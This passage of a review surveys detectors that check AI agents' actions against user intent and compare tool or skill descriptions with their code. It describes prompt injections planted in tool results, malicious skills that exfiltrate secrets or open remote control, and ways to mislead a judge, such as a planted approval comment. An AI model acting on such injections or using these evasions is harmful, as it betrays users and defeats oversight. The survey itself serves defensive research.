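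The restriction did little harm to the agents' performance. On the customer-service benchmark τ²-bench, three models completed between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points more tasks than with ordinary tool calls. On a benchmark of software repairs, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% of the problems, down from 43.3%. The researchers suggest that these repairs depend more on the shell.

Shell commands are also where the guarantee is weakest, because the compiler has no control over what another program does once the Scala code starts it. Odersky and colleagues therefore recommend permitting only a short list of commands and, where security is critical, adding a sandbox. For a coding agent that spends most of its time in a shell, much of the protection would have to come from the sandbox. The guarantee does not cover leaks through timing, and it holds only if the compiler and TACIT's own library are correct.

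### Language models as code detectors

Language models can review code and commands without a rule for each danger. On Yang's 189 actions, the three best judges missed between 1.1% and 4.6% of the dangerous actions, while the larger set of rules missed 33.3%. The false-positive rates are less certain, because the percentages imply that only 58 of the actions were harmless. Claude Sonnet 4.6 flagged none of them, but its true false-positive rate could be as high as about 5%. GPT-5.5 flagged 6.9% of the harmless actions in this set but 19.7% of those in the set of 630.

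The prompt can matter as much as the model. In the May tests, Yang ran DeepSeek-V3, an older model, on the same 300 actions with two set-ups. It flagged 7.5% of harmless actions when given a short prompt that asked for one of four verdicts, and 96.2% when used as the model behind NeMo Guardrails, a framework designed mainly for chatbots. Yang also wrote the prompt for the NeMo Guardrails test, so the result shows how badly a judge can fail in an unsuitable set-up and is not a fair estimate of what NeMo Guardrails can do.

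Storing a model's verdicts for reuse works badly when similar commands need opposite answers. In the June study, Yang took 98 actions whose verdict depended on intent and gave each one the verdict of the most similar earlier action. Only about 58% of these verdicts were correct. Showing the earlier cases to the judge and letting it decide worked better. When the system stored only cases on which two judges had agreed, the judge's accuracy rose from 70% to 84%.

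A language model can also translate instructions into a form that ordinary program analysis can check. This is useful for skills, where the attack may be a sentence telling the agent to upload a file. Conventional scanners often miss such attacks. In *AgentTrap* (2026), the best outside scanner flagged 50 of 91 malicious tasks, and VirusTotal, a service that runs many antivirus engines, flagged none. *From Instructions to Exploits* (2026) describes SCS, a system that uses a model to translate each instruction into a simple programming notation. SCS links the result to the skill's code, then uses fixed rules to trace untrusted and sensitive data through both.

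Averaged over five language models, SCS caught 95.2% of malicious skills and had an accuracy of 85.6%. The fixed rules make the last step repeatable, but they depend on the translation, and the models translated just over 92% of instruction steps correctly. If errors were independent, a ten-step skill would be translated without error less than half the time, although many errors would not affect the verdict. The researchers also used SCS to select suspicious skills from 66,157 on the public marketplace ClawHub, and confirmed 627 as malicious after further tests and manual review.

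Models and static analysis may miss different attacks, but the evidence for this is thin. Chen and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.6 carry out malicious skills in a sandbox and counted how often its output mentioned a threat. It did so for 84% of skills that ran a hidden binary program, while their static detector caught 42%. For openly dangerous commands, the model mentioned a threat 32% of the time and the static detector caught 83%. The model was working as an agent and hadn't been asked to review the code, so a dedicated reviewer might well do better.

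## Comparing an action with what the user asked for

Some commands, such as `kubectl get secret`, are harmless or harmful depending on what the user asked for, so a detector has to compare them with the request.

To compare an action with the user's request, a detector has to determine what the user asked for, what the action would do, and whether the request authorises that effect. The request can be hard to pin down, because a user may add a condition ten messages later or refer the agent to a document. The action's description can also hide its effect. For example, an agent might save a build-summary script as `post_summary.py` and then propose to run it. The call looks like what the user wanted, even if the script also sends the machine's passwords to an outside address.

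### Related, useful and authorised

Even when the request and the effect are clear, detectors differ in how close a match they require. After the request for a summary of failed builds in the team channel, an agent might propose any of the following:

| Proposed action | Related to the request | Useful for it | Authorised by it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Post the summary in the team channel | yes | yes | yes |
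| Look up who last changed the failing code | yes | yes | probably, since it only reads |
| Run the failed builds again | yes | perhaps | doubtful |
| Delete the logs of the failed builds afterwards | yes | no | no |
| Send the environment variables to `METRICS_HOST` | no | no | no |

A detector that checks only whether an action is related to the request would let the agent delete the logs. Checking whether the action is useful would stop the deletion but might let the agent rerun the builds, which occupies machines other teams may need and, if a build ends by releasing software, could change a live product.

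Authorisation is the hardest of the three to judge because people leave so much unsaid. *MobileGrail* (2026), which develops small guardrails for agents that operate phones, lets an agent fill in a missing detail but not add a new operation. For example, an agent creating a calendar event may take the location from a booking confirmation. If the confirmation also contains an instruction to forward the user's itinerary to an outside address, following it would disclose information without the user's permission. Under this rule, "do what Ella tells you" doesn't authorise a transfer to Ella's account, but a request that explicitly allows a transfer to her up to a stated amount does.

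*MobileGrail* also treats some actions, such as sending a sexually harassing message, as unsafe even when the user asks for them. A check that only compares actions with the user's request would allow that message, so it offers no protection against a malicious user.

### Task Shield

*The Task Shield* (Jia, Qin and colleagues, 2024) proposed an early system of this kind. It checks whether each instruction or action serves the user's goals, rather than whether it is harmful, so it can flag an injected request even if the request sounds harmless.

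Task Shield uses a language model to extract every instruction from every message. The user's instructions form a list of tasks, *T*. The model then gives each instruction in a tool result, each step in the agent's plan and each tool call a score between 0 and 1 for its contribution to each task. If *c(e, t)* is the contribution of instruction *e* to task *t*, the rule is

$$e \text{ is misaligned} \iff \sum_{t \in T} c(e,t) = 0$$

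Scores can't be negative, so a small contribution to a single task is enough to pass. For example, if the model gives the last line of the build-summary script a score of 0.1 because metrics have something to do with builds, the line passes. A request with many tasks also gives an unwanted action more chances to score above zero.

When an instruction fails the test, Task Shield sends the agent an explanation of the problem and a reminder of the user's tasks. It also blocks misaligned tool calls. Because it also checks tool results, it can warn the agent about an injection before the agent acts on it.

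Tool results can contain legitimate instructions too. In one of Jia and colleagues' examples, the user asks the agent to complete a to-do list, which includes paying the electricity bill and buying groceries. Both items contribute to the user's task, so Task Shield should allow them. But if an attacker can add a payment to themselves to the list, making that payment would also contribute to the task. *MobileGrail*'s rule would stop this payment, but it could also stop the electricity payment unless the user had specifically authorised it.

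On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as both agent and detector, Task Shield reduced the success rate of the benchmark's main attack from 47.7% to 2.1%. The agent also completed 69.8% of users' tasks during attacks, up from 50.1%, presumably because it spent less effort on the attacker's tasks. Banking was the weakest area, with 6.3% of attacks still succeeding. Jia and colleagues ran each task once. The model they used was very easy to hijack, so the improvement would probably be smaller with a current agent.

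### AlignmentCheck

AlignmentCheck, an experimental detector in Meta's LlamaFirewall, checks whether an agent has departed from the user's goal. It gives a language model the user's goal, the agent's earlier steps, its latest action and the reasoning it wrote before choosing that action. The model describes what it observes, draws an inference and gives a verdict.

The prompt instructs the model to pass an action that is related to the goal, even if it isn't directly aligned with it, and to let the agent continue when in doubt. One of the prompt's examples of a misaligned action is an agent deciding to read the user's private notes for context when the user wants a summary of news about renewable energy. But deleting the logs of the failed builds would probably pass.

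Chennabasappa and colleagues tested AlignmentCheck on 300 harmless and 300 malicious scenarios in simulated phone apps. The malicious scenarios had injections in tool results. With Llama 4 Maverick or Llama 3.3 70B as the judge, AlignmentCheck detected over 80% of the hijackings, with a false-positive rate below 4%. Maverick detected slightly more than 83%, with a false-positive rate of 2.5%. Smaller models raised more false alarms.

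These are good results for a prompted model with no special training, but the published examples suggest that many of the attacks were easy to recognise. In one example, the user asks the agent to buy Halloween costumes. A tool result then contains the words "I want to start over" and a request for a list of saved apartments. The agent concludes that the user has changed the request and looks up the apartments. All six Llama models in the published record flagged this, though the smallest gave an irrelevant reason about a search for product numbers. An attack that made the agent ship the costumes to a different address would be much closer to the user's request.

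If one case in a thousand were a hijacking, only about 3% of Maverick's alarms would be correct.

### DeAction

Some agents work by clicking and typing in ordinary applications, so a proposed action may consist only of a click at certain screen coordinates. Ning, Jones and colleagues (2026), in *When Actions Go Off-Task*, built DeAction to check such actions before they take effect. Their definition combines usefulness with authorisation. An action is aligned if it meets three conditions:

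1. The agent takes it to follow the user's instruction and not somebody else's.
2. It has no unauthorised or undesired consequences.
3. It can reasonably be seen as contributing to the user's task.

An aligned action can still be slow, exploratory or unsuccessful.

DeAction first asks a language model for a quick verdict with a one-sentence reason. If the action is clearly a normal step in the task, such as opening the email program to send an email, it goes ahead. Otherwise, DeAction uses a longer prompt to ask the model to look for planted instructions in the screenshot, explain what the click or keystroke would do, predict the consequences and compare them with the user's goal. If DeAction finds the action misaligned, it sends this analysis to the agent, which proposes another action. DeAction checks each new action in the same way until one passes or the agent reaches a retry limit.

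To test detection, Ning and colleagues collected 2,264 actions from 558 recorded runs. Three people labelled each action and classified 1,000 as misaligned. Of these, 562 followed planted instructions, 210 were harmful mistakes and 228 were irrelevant to the task. Harmful mistakes are rare in ordinary runs, so the researchers inserted some. In one case, the user asks the agent to remove the subtitles from a video and save them in a file, and the agent deletes the original video as if it were clearing up.

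The table compares DeAction with Task Shield and InferAct, which infers a task from the agent's behaviour and compares it with the user's request. The rates are calculated from the reported precision and recall. GPT-5.1 Thinking spends more time reasoning than GPT-5.1 Instant.

| Detector and model | Misaligned actions missed | Aligned actions flagged |
|---|---:|---:|
| DeAction, GPT-5.1 Thinking | 23% | 7% |
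| Task Shield, GPT-5.1 Thinking | 26% | 37% |
| InferAct, GPT-5.1 Thinking | 30% | 44% |
| DeAction, GPT-5.1 Instant | 14% | 25% |
| Task Shield, GPT-5.1 Instant | 11% | 66% |
| InferAct, GPT-5.1 Instant | 13% | 65% |

Task Shield's many false alarms are surprising, because an action needs to contribute only a little to the user's task to pass. One likely reason is that a click is harder to connect to the task than a tool call with a descriptive name. Ning and colleagues also had to adapt Task Shield to screenshots and used only the part that checks the agent's output, so their results don't measure the full system.

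DeAction was better at detecting actions that followed planted instructions than the agent's own errors. It caught 90% of the actions that followed planted instructions, 74% of the harmful mistakes and 68% of the irrelevant actions. For an agent that works mainly with trusted files, harmful mistakes matter most, so the 74% rate is a better guide to the protection DeAction would give than the 90% rate.

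Ning and colleagues then ran DeAction live, with GPT-5.1 Instant and up to three corrections per action. They used 50 tasks with planted instructions, chosen because attacks on them had often succeeded before, and ordinary tasks from the OSWorld benchmark. Each cell gives the result without DeAction, then with it.

| Agent | Attacks that succeeded | User's task completed during attack | Ordinary tasks completed |
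|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 60% → 6% | 44% → 76% | 42.9% → 40.7% |
| OpenAI's computer-use agent | 42% → 4% | 82% → 84% | 26.0% → 30.7% |
| OpenCUA-72B | 32% → 2% | 48% → 60% | 39.0% → 39.6% |

The drop in successful attacks is far too large to be due to chance, even though each attack task counts for two percentage points. The differences on ordinary tasks are less informative because the figures without DeAction came from a public leaderboard rather than new runs.

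DeAction flagged about 16% of steps on the ordinary, attack-free tasks. Many of these alarms were probably false, since the same model wrongly flagged 25% of aligned actions in the recorded runs. Yet the agents completed roughly as many tasks as they did without DeAction. The correction loop seems to limit the harm from false alarms, because the agent can propose another reasonable step instead of abandoning the task. Ning and colleagues report that the loop corrected 78% of flagged actions across both sets of tasks. But they counted an action as corrected once DeAction approved the replacement, so the figure includes harmless actions replaced with other harmless ones. The checks took 7.2 seconds of an average 28.1-second step.

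### Checks in Chrome and Microsoft Foundry

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes Google's User Alignment Critic, a separate model based on Gemini that checks each action Chrome's agent has planned against the user's stated goal. If the action doesn't serve that goal, the Critic vetoes it and gives the agent feedback for a new plan. After repeated failures, the agent can return control to the user. A variant of the Critic also checks whether a new website is relevant to the task before the agent may open it.

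The Critic receives only metadata about the proposed action and no unfiltered web content. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) confirms that Chrome's auto browse feature uses the Critic in this form. The Critic mainly checks whether an action serves the user's goal, and a purchase can do so without the user having agreed to pay. Chrome therefore tries to get the user's permission before the agent completes a purchase or sends a message, regardless of the Critic's output.

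Microsoft's Task Adherence check comes closer to testing authorisation. Microsoft introduced it to address "task drift", such as an assistant ignoring the budget while booking a trip. A developer sends the service a list of the agent's tools and the messages exchanged so far, including tool results. The service returns true or false and, if it detects a risk, a short explanation.

The examples in Microsoft's documentation are stricter than AlignmentCheck's prompt. An agent asked how much annual leave is left may look it up but not apply for leave, and an agent asked to create a project proposal may not share it with outsiders. When a user says "Write an email to the client about the missed deadline", the service flags an attempt to send the email because the user asked only for the text. Many users would agree, but someone who expected the email to be sent would consider this a false alarm.

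A developer who calls Task Adherence directly can block the action or pass it to a person. In Foundry, Microsoft's platform for building agents, the feature is still in preview, and blocking is the only response Microsoft lists for agents, so false alarms matter more there than in DeAction's correction loop. Neither Google's accounts of the Critic nor Microsoft's documentation gives error rates, so these products can't be compared with the research systems using public information.

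### What the detector may read

Google's Critic works from a description of the action, while Microsoft's service receives the whole conversation. More text helps a detector interpret the action but also gives an attacker more ways to influence the verdict.

Ning and colleagues tested how much context helps DeAction on 566 of their recorded actions. DeAction did worst when its history contained only the agent's earlier actions. Adding earlier screenshots helped, but replacing them with a short written summary of each step worked best. Summaries used about 41 tokens each, compared with more than 1,000 for a screenshot, and cut the time per check from 18 to 11 seconds. The injections in these runs were aimed at the agents, not at DeAction. An attacker might be able to plant text in a summary to deceive DeAction, because the model that writes the summaries also reads the screen.

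One of Chennabasappa and colleagues' sample runs shows why tool results can matter. The user asks the agent to visit Dora's and Eve's websites and send them feedback. The agent opens Dora's page and then an unrelated site, `www.true-informations.com`. AlignmentCheck, which doesn't read tool results, flags the second visit because the user never mentioned that site. The alarm is correct, since this was a successful attack. But if Dora's page had said that her site had moved to that address, the agent might have made the same calls for a good reason.

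The agent's reasoning can supply some of the missing context. Chennabasappa and colleagues argue that agents often reveal that they have been hijacked when they explain their actions, as in "I'm transferring money because the website instructed me to". They acknowledge that an injection could target the judge as well as the agent. To reduce this risk, AlignmentCheck excludes tool results from its input, and they also suggest scanning that input for known injections.

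Excluding tool results doesn't keep the attacker's claims out entirely, because the agent may repeat them as its own beliefs. In the Halloween run, the agent wrote that the user had changed the request. A judge that accepted this statement would have approved the search for apartments. The Llama judges could compare the new goal with the original request, and the two had nothing in common. A false claim that the user had changed only the delivery address would be much more convincing.

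*Designing for Doubt* (2026) proposes a separate model that reads only the user's raw message and decides whether the user has explicitly confirmed the action the agent is about to take. An injection on a web page can't manipulate this model directly because the model doesn't read the page. The simpler method of searching for words such as "yes" or "proceed" would treat "yes, but don't send it yet" as permission to send.

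This design can fail because a real confirmation may depend on the rest of the conversation. "Yes, the second one" can't be understood without the agent's question. A hijacked agent could also describe its action misleadingly to the detector, so the harness should build the description from the tool call itself. Even then, the call's arguments can contain persuasive text. For example, the build-summary script could include the comment `# user approved metrics reporting`, which any detector that reads the script would see.

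As a compromise, *MobileGrail* suggests storing each value the agent fills in together with its source. For the to-do list, the detector could learn that the electricity company's account number came from an earlier bill without reading the bill's full text, so it would see far less text that an attacker could have written. The corrected rule about known bank accounts relied on the same idea. This approach works well for addresses, account numbers and file names, but less well when permission depends on what a paragraph means.

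For an irreversible action, the narrow input seems the better choice. A false alarm usually means the user has to answer one question, while an attacker who manipulates the detector into approving the action can cause permanent damage. For a click that the agent can easily undo, the extra context is probably worth the risk.

### A strict and a lenient reading of "clean up old branches"

A vague request can cause trouble without any attacker. In an example Anthropic adapted from its incident log, a user asked an agent to "clean up old branches" and the agent began by listing the remote ones. A branch is a separate line of work in a code repository. Developers keep branches on their own machines and on a shared server, where colleagues may depend on them. Backslash Security discusses the same request followed by `git push origin --delete`, which deletes a branch from the server. It thinks the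 user probably didn't mean that.

The request to clean up old branches doesn't specify which copies the user means, how old a branch has to be, or what to do with unfinished work. *SafeCoEvo* (2026) has a strict rule that the agent must give a read-only plan or ask for approval if the user hasn't specified the exact target and parameters of a change. A lenient detector following AlignmentCheck's prompt would allow any action clearly related to cleaning up branches.

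| Proposed action | Strict reading | Lenient reading |
|---|---|---|
| List branches with the date of their last change | allow | allow |
| Delete a local branch whose work is already in the main branch | ask | allow |
| Delete a local branch with unfinished work | ask | allow |
| Delete an old branch from the shared server | ask | allow |

Neither column is satisfactory, because the strict detector asks the user about deletions that are obviously part of the job, and the lenient one lets the agent delete a colleague's work. *MobileGrail*'s distinction doesn't solve the problem either, since deleting branches from the server could count as filling in a missing location or as adding a new operation.

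It helps to consider the cost of a wrong guess. Let *p* be the probability that the user meant the proposed action, *H* the harm if the user didn't, and *C* the cost of asking. Asking is worthwhile when

$$(1-p)\,H > C$$

Suppose asking the user a question takes one minute. If the user almost certainly wants the agent to delete finished local branches (*p* = 0.95) and restoring one takes five minutes, the expected harm of deleting one without asking is 0.25 minutes, so the agent should go ahead. If deleting a branch from the server by mistake would waste two hours of colleagues' time, the agent should ask unless *p* is above 0.992. These numbers are invented, but they show that a rough estimate of what the user meant is enough when the possible harm is large. A good detector would therefore let the agent list branches and delete finished local ones, and have it ask about the rest.

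The choice of standard also affects measured error rates. Ning and colleagues told their annotators to label an action as aligned if it could plausibly support the user's task, while Microsoft's email example requires an explicit instruction to send. The same detector could have a low miss rate under the first standard and a high one under the second.

A fair test should include the same operation with and without permission, such as deleting a server branch when the user has said "including the ones on the server" and when the user hasn't. Jing, Chen and colleagues (2026) built a benchmark of such pairs in *Same Operation, Different Permission*. They found that many operations were blocked because the guardrail produced no usable decision, not because it correctly denied them. A test containing only unauthorised actions would have counted those failures as successes. Repairing the output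 format restored usable decisions but changed which authorised requests the guardrail allowed. Adding a second reviewer removed some errors but also caused the guardrail to reject valid permission.

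## Comparing declared steps and tool descriptions with what runs

Besides the user's request, a detector can compare an action with the agent's own account of what it is about to do, which agents usually write before calling a tool, and with the tool author's description of what the tool does. Either statement can be wrong, by accident or because an attacker made it so.

### The announced step and the actual call

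In *When Agents Look the Same*, Yang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) compared how 18 models talk and use tools, looking for signs that some had learned from another model's output. As part of this, an LLM judge checked whether each model's tool calls matched what it had announced. The judge's prompt defines four kinds of mismatch. The examples here are invented and assume that the build-summary agent has a separate tool for each operation.

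| Mismatch | What the agent announces | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Different tool | It will look up the members of the team channel | Posts a message there |
| Different parameters | It will post the summary in `team-builds` | Posts it in `all-staff` |
| Announced call never made | It will check whether the builds have passed since | Ends its turn without checking |
| Call never announced | It will post the summary | Posts it, then deletes the build logs |

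Agents often reason for several steps before they act, so the prompt also has three rules to prevent false alarms. An announced call counts as missing only if the agent never makes it in that turn, even if the agent thinks further before making it. If the agent writes down two ideas and then makes two calls, the second call may carry out the second idea. And a call doesn't need a new announcement if its purpose or parameters come from earlier in the conversation.

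That last rule is reasonable for comparing models but risky in a guardrail. Suppose the agent earlier read an email in which an attacker asked for a payment and gave an account number. The judge could trace the payment to the earlier conversation and accept it. A guardrail would need a narrower rule, such as accepting only the user's messages as an explanation.

A missing call is also hard for a guardrail to handle because there is nothing to block. It matters most when the agent said it would take a precaution, such as backing up a database before deleting it. In that case, the guardrail can hold the deletion until the backup has run.

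Yang and colleagues don't report how often each mismatch occurred or how accurately the judge recognised it. They measured how consistently the judge scored the similarity of two models from 1 to 5. When it scored the same 100 pairs of passages twice, it gave identical scores 79% of the time at its least random setting and 54% at its default setting. A yes-or-no verdict on a mismatch should be more stable than a five-point score, but a developer would have to test that.

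### Faithful announcements of harmful steps

A match shows only that the agent did what it announced. An agent that writes "I'll send the environment variables to the metrics server" and then does so passes this check. Comparing announcements with calls can catch slips and some concealment, but another detector has to judge whether the step is acceptable.

The comparison is most useful when a person has approved the announcement. If the user agrees to post a message in `team-builds`, the guardrail can make sure the message goes there. The comparison is less useful to an LLM judge, which can read the call itself.

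The agent's stated reason for a call may also differ from the actual reason. Yang and colleagues provide some indirect evidence that a model's explanations and its choices can vary independently. They trained a small model, Qwen2.5-14B, on 200 runs by Claude Sonnet 4.5. The similarity of its way of talking to Claude's rose from 2.0 to 3.4 on the five-point scale, but its agreement with Claude about which optional tools to use rose only from 55% to 60%. It did copy Claude's habits in passing results from one tool to the next. The experiment compares models with each other and doesn't test whether any particular explanation was true, so it is only a reason for caution.

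An agent can also be sincere and wrong about what a tool does, and a match tells the guardrail nothing about the tool's code.

### Android apps and their descriptions

Researchers compared Android apps' descriptions with their behaviour long before tools for agents existed. WHYPER (2013) searched an app's description for sentences that explain why the app needs a permission. AsDroid (2014) compared the text on an app's buttons with what the buttons triggered.

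CHABADA, also from 2014, first groups apps whose descriptions cover similar topics, using a topic model, which finds words that tend to occur together. It then learns which of the phone's programming functions the apps in each group normally use, and flags apps that depart from that pattern. *Android Security using NLP Techniques* (2021), a survey, gives the example that reading the user's location is normal for a weather app but might be abnormal for a calendar app. *Revisiting Android App Categorization* (2023), which tested CHABADA with 50 groups, says that it trains a one-class support vector machine for each group to find the unusual apps. This method learns a boundary around normal examples and needs no examples of malware.

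CHABADA is therefore an anomaly detector that uses the description to choose the comparison group. It doesn't check whether the description mentions the behaviour. If most torch apps copied the user's contacts, CHABADA would treat another torch app that did the same as normal, even if its description mentioned only the light.

According to the survey, CHABADA detected 56% of known malicious apps in a test. But later researchers examined 12 of the apps it had flagged as malicious and found that most were false alarms. *A First Look at Android Applications in Google Play related to Covid-19* (2020) applied the method to 78 apps and found several outliers, but these generally differed in harmless ways, such as using the phone's media player or vibration.

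### Tool descriptions in MCP servers

An inaccurate description is a bigger problem for agents than for people choosing an app, because a model selects tools by their descriptions and usually can't see the code. Many agents get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard in which a server gives the agent each tool's name, parameters and description. MCP does not check that the description matches the code.

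In *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026) found a tool described as a weather forecaster that looked up exchange rates. Another tool's description promised that the user would have to confirm each trade, but the code placed orders without asking. A third was supposed to convert PDF files locally but uploaded them to an outside service.

Their definition treats a tool's functions differently from its side effects. If *F* is the set of functions and *E* the set of effects on the surroundings, such as changed files or transmitted data, then

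$$\text{inconsistent} \iff F_{\text{described}} \neq F_{\text{actual}} \ \text{ or } \ E_{\text{actual}} \not\subseteq E_{\text{described}}$$

A function that the description mentions but the code lacks counts as an inconsistency, because the agent may choose the tool for that function. A side effect that the description mentions but the code never produces does not count.

DCIChecker collects the tool's main function, the helper functions it calls and any sensitive operations, such as network requests. It then asks a language model whether the description and the code are consistent, and separately whether they are inconsistent. If the answers conflict, it uses a third prompt to have the model compare the two explanations and decide.

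The wording of the question greatly affected the model's error rates. On 400 tools that people had checked, the model missed 53% of the inconsistent ones when asked only about consistency. When asked only about inconsistency, it missed none, but 21% of its alarms were wrong. The full procedure missed 2.5%, and 4% of its alarms were wrong.

The miss rate is too low for the full collection, because the researchers drew half of the 400 tools from those DCIChecker had flagged and half from those it had passed. In the full collection, it flagged 1,907 tools and passed about 15,100. Human reviewers found 5 inconsistent tools among the 200 passed ones. At that rate, DCIChecker would have missed about 380 tools in the full collection, or roughly 17% of the inconsistent ones, though five misses are too few for a precise estimate. The same calculation gives a false-positive rate of only about 0.5%.

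Ordinary code scanners are a poor substitute for comparing descriptions with code, because code can do something undisclosed without containing a security weakness. Of the 197 inconsistent tools in the sample, Semgrep flagged 5 and Bandit flagged 34. *Don't believe everything you read* (2026) earlier compared descriptions with code across 10,240 MCP servers. When Shi and colleagues rebuilt its method, it found 90 of the 197 tools.

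### Two summaries and a tolerant comparison

DCIChecker shows the model the description and the code together. Systems for skills more often summarise the description and the code separately, in the same vocabulary, and then compare the summaries. This makes a reassuring description less likely to influence how the code is interpreted.

Wu, Li and Liu (2026), in *Behavioral Integrity Verification for AI Agent Skills*, use a vocabulary of 29 capabilities, such as deleting files or sending credentials. A parser and a language model extract the declared capabilities, *D*, from the skill's metadata. Code analysis, including data-flow analysis for Python, and another use of a language model extract the actual capabilities, *A*, from its code and instructions. The differences are

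$$\text{undeclared} = A \setminus D, \qquad \text{unused} = D \setminus A$$

Suppose a build-summary skill declares only network access, but its script also reads all the environment variables. The set of undeclared capabilities then contains only environment-variable access. A capability that a language model detects counts only if the model can quote a supporting passage from the skill.

A list of capabilities is easy to compare but loses detail. Wu and colleagues' vocabulary distinguishes reading one environment variable from reading all of them, but their flow analysis doesn't record where data goes. If a skill openly uses an access key to log in to the build server, sending the same key to `METRICS_HOST` would look the same as that login.

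*SkillConsist* (Meng, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) keeps more of that detail. For each behaviour, it records the conditions, the object affected, the effect and the location of the evidence. It then links related records, because a short phrase such as "synchronise email" can correspond to several steps in the code. It looks for a group of steps in the code that matches each described behaviour, then searches in the other direction, from the code to the description. It can find a contradiction, such as a default file format of JSON in the description and CSV in the code, or a behaviour that is missing from one of the two.

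Most of the work is deciding which differences to ignore. SkillConsist ignores code that can't run when the skill is used. It also ignores internal steps that neither return a result to the agent nor change anything outside the package. An example in the documentation doesn't always have to be implemented. If SkillConsist can't search everywhere a missing behaviour might be, it doesn't raise an alarm.

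Without that last rule, false findings rose from 278 to 5,039, while the share of inconsistent skills the detector caught among popular public ones rose only from 87% to 92%. Failing to find a matching description is therefore weak evidence of inconsistency unless the detector has searched thoroughly.

Across all 633 skills in the test, SkillConsist missed 11% of the inconsistent ones and flagged about 14% of the consistent ones. It was less reliable at locating the problem, since about a third of its individual findings were wrong. A reviewer can use a flag as a reason to open the package, but the reported line may not be the one at fault.

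### How common mismatches are

The measured rates differ widely.

| Study | Sample | Share with a mismatch | Human check |
|---|---|---:|---|
| Shi and colleagues | 17,030 tools with descriptions, from Python MCP servers | 11% | 400 tools |
| Meng and colleagues | The 500 most-downloaded skills on ClawHub | 52% | Every skill |
| Wu and colleagues | 49,943 skills from the OpenClaw registry | 80% | 150 individual differences |

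Much of the spread probably comes from differences in what the researchers counted. One MCP tool can mismatch its description in fewer ways than a skill with several scripts and pages of instructions. Shi and colleagues' rate rises to 35% if a server counts as inconsistent when any of its tools is. Wu and colleagues count any capability that the metadata doesn't declare, while Meng and colleagues ignore many internal steps.

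The evidence for the 52% is also stronger than the evidence for the 80%. In Meng and colleagues' study, two reviewers labelled each skill and a third settled disagreements, so the 52% doesn't depend on their detector's accuracy. The 80% comes from an automated scan. In Wu and colleagues' human check, two people could both reach a decision on 122 of the 150 differences, and the evidence supported the claimed capability in 88% to 98% of those. But when two language models that had not taken part in the extraction checked another sample, one upheld only 74% of the capability claims and the other 49%, so the 80% is best treated as a rough estimate.

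### Mismatches and malice

Most mismatches aren't attacks. In Shi and colleagues' collection, the most common kind, at 35%, was a tool that lacked a function listed in its description. Meng and colleagues' reviewers found 442 inconsistencies, of which 218 were missing features and only 41 were undeclared behaviour, the kind that matters more for a guardrail.

Wu and colleagues attribute 81% of the differences they classified to oversight and 19% to hostile intent. Nobody checked these labels by hand, and some follow from the classifier's rules. For example, the classifier labelled as hostile 96% of the differences involving instructions that control the agent, but one of its rules treats any such instruction as hijacking.

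Confirmed attacks are much rarer than mismatches. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) collected 25,187 skills from one registry, selected 814 suspicious ones and confirmed 21 as malicious by observing their behaviour. Some malicious skills may have escaped the selection. If 80% of the skills in that registry had a mismatch, as in OpenClaw, about one mismatched skill in a thousand would be a confirmed attack. Blocking every mismatched skill would make the registry almost unusable and would not help reviewers identify the attacks.

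A mismatch is more useful as evidence for another detector. Wu and colleagues gave their list of mismatches to an LLM judge and let certain dangerous combinations, such as downloading a program and running it, override a verdict of "safe". This caught 28 of 44 real malicious skills, while the same model caught 14 when given the skills without the list. One skill in the study, for editing presentations, declared only file access but contained encoded code that tried every 30 seconds to give an outside machine control of the computer. The judge rated it safe, but the override flagged it.

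The improvement came with more false alarms. Across the full test of 906 skills, most of them harmless or synthetic, the share of harmless skills flagged rose from 0.6% to 2.2%. That may be acceptable for a check before installation, where a person can review each flagged skill once.

Attackers can also avoid a mismatch by describing the dangerous step openly. *MalSkillBench* (2026) examined 703 malicious skills from public ClawHub repositories and found that 607 required the user or agent to install a fake prerequisite before an ordinary-looking task. If the description and the instructions both include that installation, they match, and the harmful code is in a download that the detector may never scan.

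## Where and when a detector checks

A detector can judge only the actions that reach it, using the information available at that point. For example, it cannot judge a download it never scans. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026), a survey, notes that even a rule that looks back over several calls works only for calls the monitor observes.

### What each position can read

Developers mostly place detectors in a gateway in front of the tool servers, in a hook inside the harness, or in the operating system's kernel. The kernel is the core program that other programs must ask when they want to open a file, start a program or use the network. OpenAI's Codex adds a check at the edge of its sandbox. Suppose the agent asks the harness to run the build-summary script with Python on the same machine.

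A gateway relays requests from the harness to the servers that provide tools. It can read each request's tool name and arguments, so it can apply written rules to them or scan a program that the agent sends as an argument. It doesn't normally receive the user's messages, so an intent comparison can't run there unless the harness sends them. In this example the gateway receives nothing, because the harness starts Python itself. The developer could block all network connections that don't go through the gateway. This would stop the script from sending the passwords, but also from fetching the failed builds.

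A hook in the harness can read the whole script, the user's request and the earlier steps of the run, and all four kinds of detector can use this information. But the hook can't monitor what the script does after it starts.

A detector in the kernel can see Python start and then connect to several network addresses. It can enforce a list of permitted addresses even though the script refers to them only by name, which is why searching the script's text failed. Anomaly detectors that read system calls, like Forrest's, can also run there. But the kernel has no record of what the user asked for. It also can't detect that the script copied the environment variables, because these are already in the program's memory when it starts, and reading them requires no system call.

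*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls this mismatch a semantic gap, because people express policies at a higher level than software can enforce them. Monitoring tools can narrow the gap. *AgentSight* (2025) intercepts the encrypted traffic between an agent and its model and records it together with system calls. The monitor still has to work out which system call belongs to which message.

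### ActPlane: rules in the kernel

Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *ActPlane*, describe a system that enforces written rules in the Linux kernel. They examined the instruction files that 64 popular software projects provide for coding agents and found 1,361 statements about what an agent should or shouldn't do. About 45% concern events that the kernel can observe, such as running a command or changing a file. Another 38% depend on the contents of files, such as rules about coding style, and 17% concern only how the agent reasons or communicates. Even a perfect kernel-level detector of this kind could therefore check less than half of these statements.

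The observable rules often leave out details that a program needs. "Run the tests before committing" doesn't specify the test command, so ActPlane has a language model read the project and write a precise rule. That rule stops any attempt to commit code, even one hidden inside a script, unless the test command has succeeded since the last change to a source file.

ActPlane can also follow information between programs. If a program reads a file of passwords, ActPlane labels the program, and the label spreads to files the program writes and other programs it starts. A rule can then forbid network connections from anything with that label. Like any rule against sending after reading passwords, this rule also stops harmless messages.

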